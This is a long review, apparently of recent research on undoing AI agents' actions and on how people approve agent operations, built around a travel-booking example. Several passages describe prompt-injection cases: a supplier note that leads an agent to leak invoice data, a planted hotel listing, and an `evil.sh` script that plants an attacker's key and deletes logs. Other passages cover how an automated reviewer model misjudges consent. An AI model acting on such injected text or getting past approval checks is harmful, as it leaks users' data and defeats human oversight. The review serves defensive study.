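Some calls can't be delayed or undone. If the customer uses a wheelchair, the agent may have to email a hotel to ask about access and read the answer before choosing a room. The developer then has to end the transaction early, check the work so far, send the email and start a new transaction when the reply arrives. Mohammadi and colleagues recommend that a transaction cover one phase of an agent's work instead of an entire long-running task. But each early commit leaves less of the task for the final check, and an agent that constantly writes to people and waits for their answers would be checked on almost every call.

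## Which effects can be undone, and how

When a runtime lets a reservation go through immediately, it relies on being able to cancel it later. How much this matters depends on how often a run fails partway. Suppose that each of the booking agent's seven calls fails 10% of the time, independently of the others. All seven succeed with a probability of

0.9⁷ ≈ 0.48

so more than half of the runs hit at least one failure. If each call fails 30% of the time, the figure is 0.7⁷ ≈ 0.08, and only about one run in twelve gets through.

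Many of these failures do no harm. At the 10% rate, about 34% of runs fail during a search or at the hotel reservation, usually before the agent has changed anything, so it can start again. Another 18% fail after the hotel has accepted the reservation, which leaves something to undo or finish.

Retrying failed calls makes a run more likely to succeed. If each call has a 30% failure rate and the agent can retry it three times, all four attempts fail only 0.8% of the time (0.3⁴), and all seven calls succeed in about 94% of runs. This calculation assumes that a failed attempt changes nothing, which is wrong if the airline sold the seat and only its reply got lost. The runtime therefore needs a record of whether each call is safe to repeat and what would reverse it.

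### The class of each booking call

In Atomix, developers supply this information in an adapter, a short piece of code for each tool that averages about 17 lines. The adapter names the resource that the call affects and gives the call an idempotency key, an identifier that lets the runtime recognise a repeat of the same call. It also assigns the effect to a class: reversible, bufferable or irreversible. Mohammadi and colleagues add a variant for effects that are reversible at a cost, and they put the reservations in their own holiday example there. The seven calls then look like this:

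| Call | Class | When it runs | If the transaction aborts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1–3. Search for flights, hotels and cars | No effect | Immediately | Nothing to undo |
| 4. Reserve the hotel | Reversible with cost | Immediately | Cancel, possibly for a fee |
| 5. Reserve the flight | Reversible with cost | Immediately | Cancel and claim the refund |
| 6. Reserve the car | Reversible with cost | Immediately | Cancel, possibly for a fee |
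| 7. Email the customer | Irreversible | At commit | Discard the unsent email |

None of the seven is bufferable, but saving the itinerary to a local file would be.

Calls to the same tool can belong to different classes. Many hotels offer a cheaper, nonrefundable rate, and a `reserve_hotel` call at that rate is effectively irreversible, so the runtime should hold it until commit. The agent would then have to plan the rest of the trip with only a placeholder for the hotel. Atomix's adapters assign the class based on the call's arguments, so a developer could treat refundable and nonrefundable rates differently.

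### An abort, step by step

Suppose the agent has made all three reservations and queued the email. A final check then finds that the flight lands at 23:40, after the car-rental desk has closed. Suppose also that the car reservation includes the flight number. Atomix undoes the work in reverse dependency order, which means that it reverses an effect before the effects it depended on:

1. It discards the email, which never left the queue.
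2. It cancels the car.
3. It cancels the flight.
4. It cancels the hotel, which charges a fee of 40.

Cancelling the flight before the car would leave the rental firm, at least briefly, with a reservation for a passenger who is no longer on the flight. If the car cancellation failed, the customer would be left with an unwanted reservation.

Atomix also records how each effect ended. An outcome is *clean* if the compensation worked and *leaked* if an irreversible effect happened before the abort. It is *unresolved* if the compensation failed, if nobody wrote one, or if a reversible-with-cost effect left something behind, such as the hotel's fee. The abort above would therefore count as unresolved even though every cancellation worked, which seems right because the fee of 40 still has to be paid. Atomix reports leaked and unresolved outcomes to the operator.

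### How well Atomix recovers from faults

Mohammadi and colleagues tested recovery on τ-bench's retail tasks, with GPT-4.1 as the agent, by making individual tool calls fail at random. Some faults stopped a call before it ran, some lost the reply after the tool had acted, some delivered the same call twice, and some occurred during a compensation. A run counted as clean if the agent solved the task and left no duplicates, stray effects or unfinished compensations.

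| Method | No faults (10 tasks) | 10% faults (30 tasks) | 30% faults (30 tasks) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Atomix | 60% | 73% | 57% |
| Checkpoint replay | 60% | 63% | 53% |
| Compensation alone | 60% | 37% | 7% |
| No transaction | 50% | 27% | 0% |

Checkpoint replay restores the agent's saved state and reruns the calls. Four other methods, which used combinations of locks, logs and confirmation steps, scored between 3% and 7% at the highest fault rate.

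At 30% faults, the gap between Atomix and most of its rivals is far too large to be chance, but the gap between Atomix and checkpoint replay is a single task, 17 against 16. The two were also statistically tied in a larger comparison of 114 runs each at 10% faults. Small samples affect the other figures too. Atomix did better with 10% faults than with none, presumably because the first column covers only ten tasks.

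Most of Atomix's lead comes from cases where replies are lost. When Mohammadi and colleagues injected only lost replies, at a rate of 10%, Atomix completed 63% of tasks cleanly, compared with 43% for compensation alone and 30% for the unprotected agent. With only duplicate deliveries, the unprotected agent completed 73% cleanly and Atomix 67%.

Other results suggest that the main test somewhat overstates Atomix's benefit. When faults arrived in bursts of three, at an average rate of about 12%, the agent completed 60% of tasks without protection and 67% with Atomix. Real faults often come in bursts, because a service that is down for one call tends to be down for the next. Mohammadi and colleagues describe their fault rates as a stress setting, not an estimate of production rates.

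The simpler methods' near-total failure on τ-bench also doesn't extend to every setting. One of them takes a lock, logs the old values and restores them after a failure. At a 30% fault rate, it scored only 3% on τ-bench, but 48% on website tasks (Atomix scored 57%) and 32% on desktop tasks (Atomix scored 37%). There were only ten website tasks and seven desktop tasks. Mohammadi and colleagues built every rival method themselves inside a common test program, so the scores do not measure any commercial product.

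### Emails that should not go out

Checkpoint replay's tie with Atomix breaks down when an effect is irreversible. To show this, Mohammadi and colleagues connected an agent to a real mail and web endpoint that kept everything it received. In each trial, the agent asked to send an email in a transaction that then aborted. They used five reasons for the abort, with 100 trials of each:

- a tool failed
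- a call timed out
- the final check rejected the work
- somebody else changed data that the agent had read
- the runtime was exploring several plans at once and chose a different one

| Method | Invalid emails sent, out of 500 |
|---|---|
| Atomix | 0 |
| Checkpoint replay | 200 |
| Atomix with the email misclassified | 300 |
| Compensation alone | 400 |
| No transaction | 500 |

Every method also delivered all 500 emails in a matching set of valid transactions, so Atomix did not reach zero by blocking everything.

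With compensation alone, the email went out in every trial except those where the final check rejected the work, and there was no way to recall it. Checkpoint replay sent the message again after tool failures and timeouts because it reran the calls. A customer whose agent restarts twice could receive three confirmations for one trip, or a confirmation for a trip that never happened.

Two simpler methods, the lock and log and Try-Confirm-Cancel, also leaked nothing. In Try-Confirm-Cancel, a developer writes three handlers for each tool, to prepare an action, confirm it or cancel it. Holding the email is evidently what prevents the leak, and a developer can do that without Atomix. Atomix's claimed advantage is less work, at about 17 lines of code per tool, compared with about 30 for the lock and log and 50 for Try-Confirm-Cancel. The two simpler methods leaked nothing only because Mohammadi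 and colleagues had written the extra code for the email tool.

The 300 leaks after misclassification are probably the most important figure for anyone who wants to use such a system. Atomix enforces whatever class the developer chose and cannot detect a wrong choice. This mistake is easy to make. For example, a developer might label `reserve_hotel` as reversible when the hotel's system emails the guest a confirmation as soon as it accepts a reservation. The customer then receives an email that nobody can recall, even though the agent never called an email tool.

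### Restoring files

Files are easier to restore than bookings because the runtime can keep the old contents. Git already does something similar by recording versions of a project's files. Chen and colleagues compared Git with Cordon, which keeps an agent's file changes in a private copy until commit. They scripted five failures with no language model involved and ran 15 trials. Each trial carried out a bad step, rolled it back and tested whether the task could continue.

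| Method | Median rollback time | Median differences left behind | Trials that could continue |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cordon | 4.17 ms | 0 | 15 of 15 |
| Git restore | 10.99 ms | 73 | 0 of 15 |
| Git reset | 12.27 ms | 73 | 0 of 15 |
| Git reset and clean | 21.74 ms | 0 | 12 of 15 |

Git's `restore` and `reset` commands put back the files that Git tracks, but they leave any new files the agent created. Adding `clean` deletes the new files. The combination still failed in the task where the agent had changed a file's permissions, which Git mostly doesn't record. In ordinary use, `clean` can also delete new files that belong to the user.

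Cordon's main advantage is that it restored everything, although five scripted failures are a narrow test. Its rollback was also the fastest, but the whole recovery, including the failed step and the test afterwards, took 179 milliseconds with Cordon and 100 to 111 with Git. This difference matters little because a single call to the model takes far longer than either recovery.

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) collects 290 public reports of agents misusing files. Among the reports that made clear whether the user could recover, 40% described a permanent loss, 29% a recovery that took substantial effort and 31% an easy one. About 42% of the cases with actual harm or a demonstrated attack involved files outside the project folder, which Git normally doesn't track. An agent can also delete Git's own history, since Git stores it in an ordinary folder.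 The 40% figure probably overstates how often damage is permanent, because people are more likely to report disasters than small mishaps.

Their response is YoloFS, a filesystem that sits between the agent and the real files. It keeps new file contents in a separate store. It also maintains a map that links each file name to new contents, to the original file or to nothing, and a journal of every change to that map. Suppose an agent runs a code formatter that secretly deletes a guide and rewrites a source file:

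1. YoloFS has already taken a snapshot after the previous command, by adding a marker to the journal.
2. The formatter runs. YoloFS links the source file's name to the rewritten contents and the guide's name to nothing. The real files do not change.
3. The agent receives a list of the files that the command created, changed or deleted.
4. If the agent decides that the deletion was a mistake, it asks to return to the snapshot. YoloFS replays the journal up to the marker and rebuilds the earlier map, and the guide reappears.

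A snapshot adds little overhead because YoloFS doesn't copy the disk. It makes a new copy of a changed file only when a program opens that file for writing after a later snapshot. It also keeps the history the agent abandoned, so the agent can reverse a mistaken undo. Only the user can commit the changes to the real files.

Zhong and colleagues tested YoloFS on 11 routine-looking commands with hidden destructive effects, using Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6. Without YoloFS, the damage went through in 10 of the 11 tasks. With it, the agent noticed and undid the damage in 8 tasks, without being prompted to look for destructive changes. In one, a tool that should only have checked the code for errors deleted two files, and the agent remarked that this was unusual and undid the deletion.

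In the other three tasks the agent accepted the damage. One deployment script copied the source code to another folder and then deleted the original, which the agent took for normal deployment behaviour. The changes still needed the user's approval, so the user could reject them. Undo therefore helps only if the agent or the user recognises the mistake. Mistakes were fairly easy to recognise in this test because each project had between 10 and 41 lines of code. A missing folder would be harder to spot in a list of 500 changed files.

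YoloFS can undo only changes to files. If the formatter had uploaded the source code to a website, returning to the snapshot would not have removed it from the website. Reading a secret, such as a password, can't be undone either, so YoloFS blocks access to sensitive files until the user allows it.

### Earlier designs for agents that undo their work

Researchers had proposed undo for agents before these systems, with different ideas about what to do when it is unavailable. In *GoEX*, Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) argued that people find it easier to judge an action's result than the code before it runs. GoEX therefore runs the action first and lets the user reverse it afterwards. Sometimes the runtime has to prepare for this, for example by saving a local copy of an email before deleting the original.

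GoEX uses permissions to limit the possible damage from actions it cannot reverse. A user might let the agent read email but not send it, or order a pizza but not touch a bank account. This is safe, but it also blocks useful actions. The booking agent would be unable to send its confirmation email, whereas Atomix can send it once the trip has committed.

*SagaLLM* (2025) deals with the risk that an agent no longer knows how to compensate. A model in a long task may lose track of the reservation number, the reason for a choice or the conditions for a refund. SagaLLM stores this information outside the model, along with a graph of how the operations depend on each other. Each entry in the graph has the form

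(oᵢ, oⱼ, cᵢⱼ)

which means that operation oⱼ depends on operation oᵢ under condition cᵢⱼ. For the booking, oᵢ could be the flight reservation, oⱼ the car reservation, and cᵢⱼ the condition that the customer collects the car at the airport. If the flight falls through, the graph shows that the car has to go too. If the customer had planned to collect the car in the city and travel there by train, it might not.

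STRATUS adds a test for whether to undo. A different group, Chen, Pan and colleagues (2025), in *STRATUS*, built it to repair faults in cloud services, where a bad repair can make an outage worse. It measures the severity of a system's state *s* as

μ(s) = w₁|A| + w₂|V| + w₃|L|

where |A| is the number of active alerts, |V| the number of broken service commitments, |L| the number of unhealthy machines, and the w's are positive weights. STRATUS records the state, carries out up to 20 commands and measures the severity again. It commits if the severity is no higher than before, and otherwise undoes the commands.

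In one STRATUS example, the severity starts at 15. The agent shuts down a service, installs a faulty version and restarts it, raising the severity to 24 and then 30. STRATUS undoes the repair, and the severity returns to 15. Another repair raises the severity from 12 to 18 before lowering it to 9, and STRATUS commits it. STRATUS compares severity at the end of a repair, so a repair can temporarily make things worse, as many good repairs do.

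STRATUS records each command and the state of the affected resource on a stack, and undoes the newest command first. It refuses any command it cannot undo, or replaces it with one it can, for example by moving a file to backup storage instead of deleting it. Each commit leaves the severity no higher than before, and each undo restores it exactly, so the severity between transactions can never exceed its starting value.

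On two benchmarks of cloud failures, STRATUS had at least 1.5 times the success rate of earlier agents. Its developers attribute much of this to letting the agent try a repair, undo it and try another. The tests used GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini and Llama 3, which are now old models. *Advancements in Cloud-Native Systems* (2026), a review of the field, reports that the evidence for such practices comes mainly from code repositories and test environments.

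### Effects that outlast an undo

The proof about STRATUS assumes that an undo restores the earlier state exactly, which its developers acknowledge is not always practical. The proof also doesn't cover what happens before the undo. In the failed repair, the other agents never see the rise from 15 to 30, because they see only the states between transactions. But customers can't use the service while it is shut down, and undoing the repair doesn't restore the ten minutes of service they lost.

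Atomix has the same limitation whenever it makes a reservation immediately. If the agent books a hotel's last room and then cancels, the room becomes available again, but a traveller turned away in the meantime may already have booked elsewhere. Mohammadi and colleagues accept this limitation so that Atomix can work with services that haven't been modified for agents. The harm is small when a hotel room is held for a minute, but it could be large if the agent reserves a clinic's last appointment or briefly publishes a wrong price.

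Compensation can also fail. A cancellation is another tool call, and the hotel's system may be down or the deadline for free cancellation may have passed. When Mohammadi and colleagues made compensations fail 30% of the time, 43 of 600 transactions left something behind. Atomix correctly flagged all of them. With the flagging switched off, a similar run reported 36 unclean transactions as clean. Flagging is useful even when the undo fails, because an operator who knows about a leftover reservation can call the hotel.

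A crash can leave it unclear whether there is anything to undo. If the runtime crashes just after releasing an email, it may have no record of whether the email went out. Sending it again could produce a duplicate, but doing nothing could leave the customer uninformed. Cordon resends the email only if there is evidence that the first attempt never completed. Otherwise it records the available information and leaves the case for a person to resolve.

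The hardest case is a transaction with two irreversible actions on separate services. Suppose a customer needs to pay for a flat on an island by bank transfer and buy a non-refundable ferry ticket to get there. The runtime can hold both actions until commit, but then it has to release one first. If the second is rejected, the customer has either paid for a flat she can't reach or bought a ticket to an island where she has nowhere to stay. Checking both services beforehand reduces the risk but can't remove it, because the last ticket may sell between the check and the purchase.

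Mohammadi and colleagues call the result a partial commit. Atomix retries the failed action a limited number of times, then stops and records which actions succeeded and which failed. A partial commit can be avoided only if at least one of the services offers a binding hold, such as a ferry ticket reserved for an hour. The hold replaces an irreversible purchase with a reversible reservation and a later confirmation.

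Without a hold, the order of actions still matters. Atomix releases actions in the order the agent requested them, so an agent should start with the one most likely to fail. If ferry tickets often sell out and bank transfers rarely fail, it should buy the ticket before paying for the flat.

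## What a person approves in a whole transaction

A person is often the last check before an agent takes an irreversible action. Wang, Li and Tian (2026) examined 21 production agent systems in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* and found that 15 ask the user to approve individual operations while the agent is working. A runtime that groups calls can instead request approval for several at once, which is called batched approval. It can do this before the program runs, partway through, or just before the commit.

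### Three moments of approval

Before the booking program runs, the customer can read it or a plain summary of it: find the cheapest flight, hotel and car, and if they cost no more than 1,200 together, reserve all three and email her. She can object to the approach, for example if she would rather pay more to be near the beach. Nothing has been reserved yet, so if she refuses, there is nothing to undo. But she doesn't know which hotel she will get or what it will cost, and she can't tell from the program that a hotel review contains an injection.

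After the searches, the request can contain actual values: a hotel for 400, a flight for 500 and a car for 200. She can now turn down a particular hotel, but she still can't know whether the airline will accept the reservation.

What she sees just before the commit depends on which effects the runtime has held back. If it makes reservations immediately, as Atomix does, she sees three confirmed reservations and an unsent email with its recipient and text. Refusing then requires cancelling the reservations, possibly for a fee. If the runtime has held back the reservations too, refusing is free, but the flight may sell out after she approves.

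For changes to files, the last moment is the most informative. Zhong and colleagues give the example of an agent that runs a script called `evil.sh`. An ordinary permission request shows only the command. YoloFS, their filesystem for agents, runs the script on staged files and then lists what the script did: it added an attacker's key to the list of keys that can log in to the computer, deleted a security log, and moved itself to a file that runs whenever the user opens a terminal.

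In a long task, though, a single review at the end comes too late to save much work, because one early mistake can spoil everything that follows and force a restart. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, a study of how software practitioners handle permission requests, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) cite an experiment by Zhou, Roy and colleagues in which 48 participants preferred confirming intermediate steps to confirming only at the end.

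### How Quasar groups its requests

Quasar, the restricted language that can see several pending calls at once, asks for approval during the run. Mell and colleagues give the algorithm, which works as follows:

1. Quasar finds every external call whose arguments are all known.
2. It asks the user to approve all of these calls in one request.
3. If the user refuses, the program ends. If she approves, Quasar starts all the calls.
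4. When the program can go no further without new calls, Quasar returns to step 1.

Approving the booking one call at a time takes seven prompts. Quasar needs three if the searches don't depend on each other, the reservations don't either, and the email waits for the reservations. The first prompt covers the three searches, the second the three reservations, and the third the email.

The number of prompts depends on how the program expresses the order of its calls. Quasar's core rules alone would put the email in the same batch as the reservations. That takes only two prompts, but the email might confirm the reservations before they are made. PopPy's cautious default would take five prompts: one for the searches, one for each reservation and one for the email. Rules that keep calls in a safe order can therefore undo much of the batching. A designer could avoid this by separating approval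 from execution. The arguments of all three reservations are known after the searches, so the runtime could request approval for them together and then make them in order.

Refusing a batch ends the program but does not undo earlier batches. If the customer refuses the email in the third request, she still has a hotel, a flight and a car.

Mell and colleagues compared Quasar with a Python interpreter that requires user approval for every external call. On GQA, a set of questions about images, and on AgentDojo, Quasar reduced user interactions by an average of 26%. Only 50% of the GQA tasks and 57% of the AgentDojo tasks had calls that Quasar could batch, and on those tasks the reductions were 53% and 44%.

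On 80 tasks from BrowseComp-Plus, a research benchmark with about 100 documents per task, the number of approval prompts fell by 97%. Programs for these tasks make many calls to a second model, and few of those calls depend on each other.

These figures probably overstate the reduction in prompts for an ordinary user. The GQA and BrowseComp-Plus programs mostly call other models to examine images or text, and few people would want to approve each of those calls. If the booking agent could search without permission, the one-by-one method would need four prompts and Quasar two. The comparison also only counts prompts, so it doesn't show whether people judge three reservations as well when they see them together as when they see them separately.

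### How carefully people review requests

Reducing the number of prompts matters because people tend to stop reading them, which researchers call approval fatigue. In March 2026, Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users accepted 93% of permission prompts in Claude Code. In August, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* put the figure at 97%. These rates alone don't show that users are inattentive, because most requests are for routine commands that a careful reviewer would also approve.

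In a more revealing experiment from the August article, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study, and partway through each session the text of one permission request changed to a command meant to be obviously dangerous. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Testers who click through quickly may see more prompts, which could explain part of the decline. The testers also worked in a practice environment, so they had less to lose than they would with their own code. Even with these caveats, the overall refusal rate was very low.

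Zhong and colleagues collected 290 reports of agents damaging or leaking files, and problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the agent acted without an approval prompt, often because the user had switched prompts off to avoid answering hundreds in a session. In 31, including a few of the same reports, the prompt did not make clear what the command would do. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it lets the agent run any code in the file. Batching approvals could make users less tempted to switch prompts off, but five obscure commands are no clearer in one list than in five separate prompts.

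Users have other ways to avoid prompts, such as an "always allow" button. Wang and colleagues point out that each use quietly widens what the agent can do, and that current products have no systematic way to narrow it again. According to Anthropic, 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks bypassed.

Salerno and colleagues asked practitioners about permissions in 18 interviews and a survey of 115 people. Of the 107 who answered the survey's permission questions, about 48% said they read requests carefully, 34% said they skim them and 21% said they approve by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. One interviewee was worried about permissions at first but "stopped caring" after many similar requests. Another said he would not read anything under a tight deadline.

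In the same survey, about 77% of respondents said they look more closely at requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges, and 64% said the same of unexpected requests. The respondents were volunteers describing their own behaviour, and Anthropic's testers suggest that people may be less vigilant in practice. Salerno and colleagues also warn against software that learns a user's preferences from past approvals, since many of those approvals may reflect tiredness or time pressure.

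Setting rules in advance has not solved the problem either. Salerno and colleagues describe an experiment by Yan in which 113 people supervised an agent through a simulated day. Rules the participants wrote blocked less overreach than either approving each action or having a model review it. Participants often set their rules to "ask", so they still had to decide when prompted, and they then explicitly approved most of the actions that went too far.

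Anthropic responded by removing the person from routine decisions. Claude Code's auto mode became the default for new sessions on individual and team plans in August 2026. It lets the agent read files and edit those inside the project, while a second model reviews everything else, such as shell commands and web requests. The second model receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tool results or the agent's explanations. Hostile text in a web page therefore can't reach it directly, and the agent's explanations can't influence its decisions.

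In the experiment with the testers, auto mode blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands (89%), including 800 that a tester had approved. Testers caught only 6 that auto mode had allowed, so adding the testers as a second check would have raised the total to 943.

Auto mode did worse in the earlier March evaluation. It wrongly blocked only 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls, but it let through 17% of 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted. These are Anthropic's figures for its own product, and the favourable comparison is with people who were barely paying attention. Anthropic acknowledges that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who carefully reviews every action, and it still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

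People seem more willing to object to larger decisions. Anthropic reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. This is encouraging for approval before a run, but it does not show that people are good at spotting dangerous plans, since a user may reject a plan because she wants a different design.

### Showing the consequence of an action

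Even a careful reviewer can make a bad decision if the approval prompt leaves out important facts. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send an outside auditor only the summary totals. An injection in a supplier's note makes the agent copy the full invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks for permission to send the file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so a prompt that shows only this call gives the user no reason to refuse.

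Their alternative, the Cumulative Consent Ledger, displays four things:

- the user's original restriction, word for word
- the exact action, taken from a trusted record of the agent's calls and not from the agent's own description
- a statement of the combined consequence, in this case that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor
- links to the earlier events that support the statement

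The ledger does not label the action a violation. The user has to compare the consequence with her own instructions.

Hossain and colleagues tested the design on 80 unpaid volunteers recruited through social media. A different group of 20 used each of the four interfaces. After two practice trials, each volunteer made 12 decisions, for 960 decisions in total. Half of the requests were legitimate and half broke the user's restrictions. The tasks involved email and calendars, cloud documents, and purchasing, and had up to 12 steps. The volunteers also answered comprehension questions and filled in a standard questionnaire about how demanding the work felt.

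| Interface | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Comprehension | Median time | Workload score |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 57.1% | 16.3 s | 27.3 |
| With exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 67.9% | 23.4 s | 31.6 |
| With restriction and full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 76.7% | 38.6 s | 44.3 |
| Consequence ledger | 24.2% | 85.8% | 81.7% | 33.2 s | 43.0 |

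The ledger and the full log contained the same facts, so the last two rows differ only in how the interface organised them. Ledger users approved 29 of 120 unsafe requests and log users approved 39. After statistical adjustment, the difference was 7.9 percentage points in the ledger's favour, but the 95% interval ran from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse. The ledger may therefore make no difference to unsafe approvals. The evidence that it saved time is slightly stronger. The estimated saving was about five seconds per decision, and the interval just excluded zero.

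Most of the improvement came from giving people more information, but both detailed interfaces took at least twice as long as the short description and felt much more demanding. Legitimate approvals also fell slightly at each step, so part of the improvement may come from people becoming more suspicious in general.

The ledger did not help in the most complicated cases, where a violation depended on a connection across several steps. Users of each interface approved 7 of 30 such unsafe requests. Hossain and colleagues suggest that a single statement may be too short to explain such a chain, and that a diagram or a step-by-step account might work better.

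Hossain and colleagues' volunteers refused 45% of unsafe requests even with the short description, far more than Anthropic's testers. This is unsurprising, because reviewing was their only task and half the requests were unsafe. Real users may see one dangerous request in hundreds, and Hossain and colleagues expect habit to become the main problem there. They also did not preregister their analysis.

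A user who trusts a confident but wrong summary may approve something she would have questioned in a raw log. The study did not test this risk, because every consequence statement was correct. In a separate test without human reviewers, the software behind the ledger recognised 107 of 120 violations, missed 7 and reported that it lacked the evidence to judge the other 6. When it received incomplete records of the agent's actions, it recognised only about 64% of the violations that depended on earlier steps. Hossain and colleagues therefore want every statement to link to its evidence and any missing evidence to be marked as missing, and they call for a study with deliberately faulty summaries.

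That software can also block actions without asking anyone. With Llama-3.1-8B, a small model from 2024, as the agent, blocking cut the malicious runs that caused unauthorised effects from 52 of 120 to 6, while legitimate completions fell from 104 to 100. Hossain and colleagues suggest that software should handle the clear cases and send the uncertain ones to a person with a note of what evidence is missing. This seems a better use of people's attention than asking them about everything, especially given the results from Anthropic's testers.

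A consequence statement could also help with the planted hotel listing, which has got past most of the automatic checks. Just before the commit, an ordinary approval request would show a hotel that costs 400 and is within budget, and the customer would probably approve it. A better request would add that the search had returned two similar hotels for less, and that the agent's choice relied on text the hotel wrote about itself. The runtime would have to record both facts, and the second is difficult to establish if the model read all the listings and picked one.

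### Tying an approval to particular actions

A well-informed approval can still cause harm if the runtime applies it too broadly. In an example from Zhong and colleagues, a user asks Codex to replace one word in one file. Codex shows a script and offers the option to approve it and skip future prompts for `sed -i`, a command that edits files in place. A user who chooses this option may also be allowing later edits that she has never seen.

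Auto mode's reviewing model makes a related mistake. In most of the missed cases Anthropic examined, it recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a request to clean up a set of code changes is not permission to overwrite the project's shared history. In other cases, the model treated approval of one action as approval of a later, similar one.

Cordon has a rule against this. Chen and colleagues require each human approval to apply to one transaction object, one action, one destination and one period of time. If the customer approves her confirmation email, this has several consequences:

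- The agent can't use the approval for next month's trip.
- It can't treat the approval as permission to order an airport transfer.
- It can't send the email to `desk@visa-check.example`.
- It has to ask again if the approval expires before the email goes out.

The outbox holds the email while the customer reviews it, and her approval gives the agent no wider authority. By contrast, ordinary tool-level approval of `send_email` may let the agent send any message to anyone.

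The approval also has to cover the message's content, or the agent could add the customer's passport number after she has approved the message. Hossain and colleagues bind each approval to the exact arguments that the user reviewed and check again if those arguments change. They cite Yang Wang's *Approval laundering* (2026), which shows that the action a user approves in a coding agent can differ from the one that runs.

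Exact binding can be inconvenient when the outside world changes. If the hotel's price rises from 400 to 405 while the customer is reading, a strict runtime has to prompt her again, even though she would almost certainly accept the new price. She could instead approve any price up to 420 for that hotel and those dates, which is still precise enough for software to enforce.

A refusal needs a clear scope too. Salerno and colleagues interviewed a practitioner who refused several requests from Codex. It then stopped asking and continued another way, and he couldn't tell whether the new approach respected his wishes. Users often want the agent to find another way, for example when it can finish without the file they refused to let it open. But refusing access to a password file might mean "don't read this file" or "don't do anything that requires my password". Salerno and colleagues recommend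 that tools let users say which they mean.

### How large a batch should be

A large batch interrupts the user less often and lets her compare the items. If her flight arrives on 3 June and her hotel booking starts on 4 June, each reservation looks fine separately, but she may notice the missing night when she sees both. Batching a small group of related calls can therefore improve her judgement as well as save time.

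These advantages weaken as the batch grows. The median decision with the consequence ledger took 33 seconds. At that rate, seven items would take about four minutes and 100 would take 55. The true figures would probably be lower, because items in one task share a history, but few people would read 100 items closely. Someone who examines ten of them and skims the rest has roughly a one-in-ten chance of examining a single bad item placed at random. An attacker who controls the agent could lower that chance by padding the batch with harmless calls.

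All-or-nothing refusal adds pressure to approve. Suppose that each item in a batch is acceptable 95% of the time, independently of the others. The chance that all 20 items are acceptable is

0.95²⁰ ≈ 0.36

so a strict reviewer would have to refuse about 64% of such batches. Under Quasar's algorithm, each refusal ends the program, including the 19 calls that may have been fine. A user who has waited for the agent to finish most of a task may well let a doubtful item through to avoid starting again.

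Letting the user refuse single items would relieve some of this pressure, but the runtime has to track which items depend on each other. If she removes the car, for example, the flight and hotel can stay, but the email may need new wording. A dependency graph like SagaLLM's could show her these effects before she decides. The runtime would then have to check the smaller transaction again, because a trip without a car might break a rule that the original trip satisfied.

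The runtime could also shorten the list without grouping unrelated decisions, by leaving out harmless searches and automatically refusing clear violations. It could put irreversible actions first. Salerno and colleagues similarly recommend that prompts show whether the user can reverse an action and warn more strongly when she can't. Grouping similar items is riskier. "Delete 500 temporary files" is easier to read than 500 file names, but it hides any file that isn't temporary. "Send two emails" would hide the attacker's address in the booking example.

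None of these studies tested how well people judge batches of different sizes. Hossain and colleagues' volunteers and Anthropic's testers each judged one request at a time, and Chen and colleagues ran Cordon with preset approval policies. A direct test could give reviewers the same 20 calls one at a time, in groups of five, and all together, include a bad call in only a few of the sessions, and measure which bad calls they catch and how long they take.

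## What restriction costs in completed tasks

Restrictions can prevent an agent from finishing a task in three ways. The model may write a program that the restricted language doesn't accept. It may write a valid program that lacks a necessary step, for example because it had to plan a hotel booking before it could see that the hotel requires a deposit. Or the program may be correct, but a policy may block an email to the hotel because the address came from a web page.

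Most published completion rates combine the losses from different restrictions, but a few experiments come close to separating them. Mell and colleagues changed the language and little else. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL without any policies, so most of the drop in their agents' completed tasks came from planning in advance. Garby and colleagues compared CaMeL with its policies on and off, and *SPA* reports the same comparison for its own labels.

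### Writing in a smaller language

Mell and colleagues had GPT-5 write programs for 1,000 questions about images from the GQA dataset and for 93 AgentDojo tasks, first with all of Python available and then with instructions to use only the part of Python that compiles to Quasar. GPT-5 wrote a complete program in advance in both versions, so the comparison doesn't measure any loss in completed tasks from planning early.

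| | Correct on GQA | Correct on AgentDojo | Ran without errors on AgentDojo |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary Python | 71.8% | 64.5% | 76.3% |
| Python subset | 71.4% | 63.4% | 82.8% |
| Subset, with compiler errors fed back | 72.3% | 67.7% | 89.2% |

With the subset, agents correctly answered about four fewer questions per 1,000 on GQA and completed 59 AgentDojo tasks instead of 60. Differences this small could easily be due to chance.

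When GPT-5 was shown its compiler errors and could try again, it completed 63 AgentDojo tasks in the restricted subset, three more than in ordinary Python. The Python version got no second attempt, so this doesn't show that the subset is better.

Small models have more trouble staying within the subset. GPT-4.1-nano answered 65% of the GQA questions correctly with instructions alone. After training on 900 examples written by GPT-5, it answered 71% of a separate set of 100 correctly, and the share of its programs that ran without errors rose from 92% to 99%. The training may have taught it something about the questions as well as the language. Mell and colleagues report no score for this model with ordinary Python, so the test does not show how much the subset lowered its accuracy, or whether stronger models lose less.

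The tasks were fairly simple. A typical GQA program finds the drinks in a picture and uses a second model to check whether each one contains alcohol, which takes one loop and one condition. The result is good evidence that a restricted language can handle short programs like the booking, but weaker evidence that it can handle long ones.

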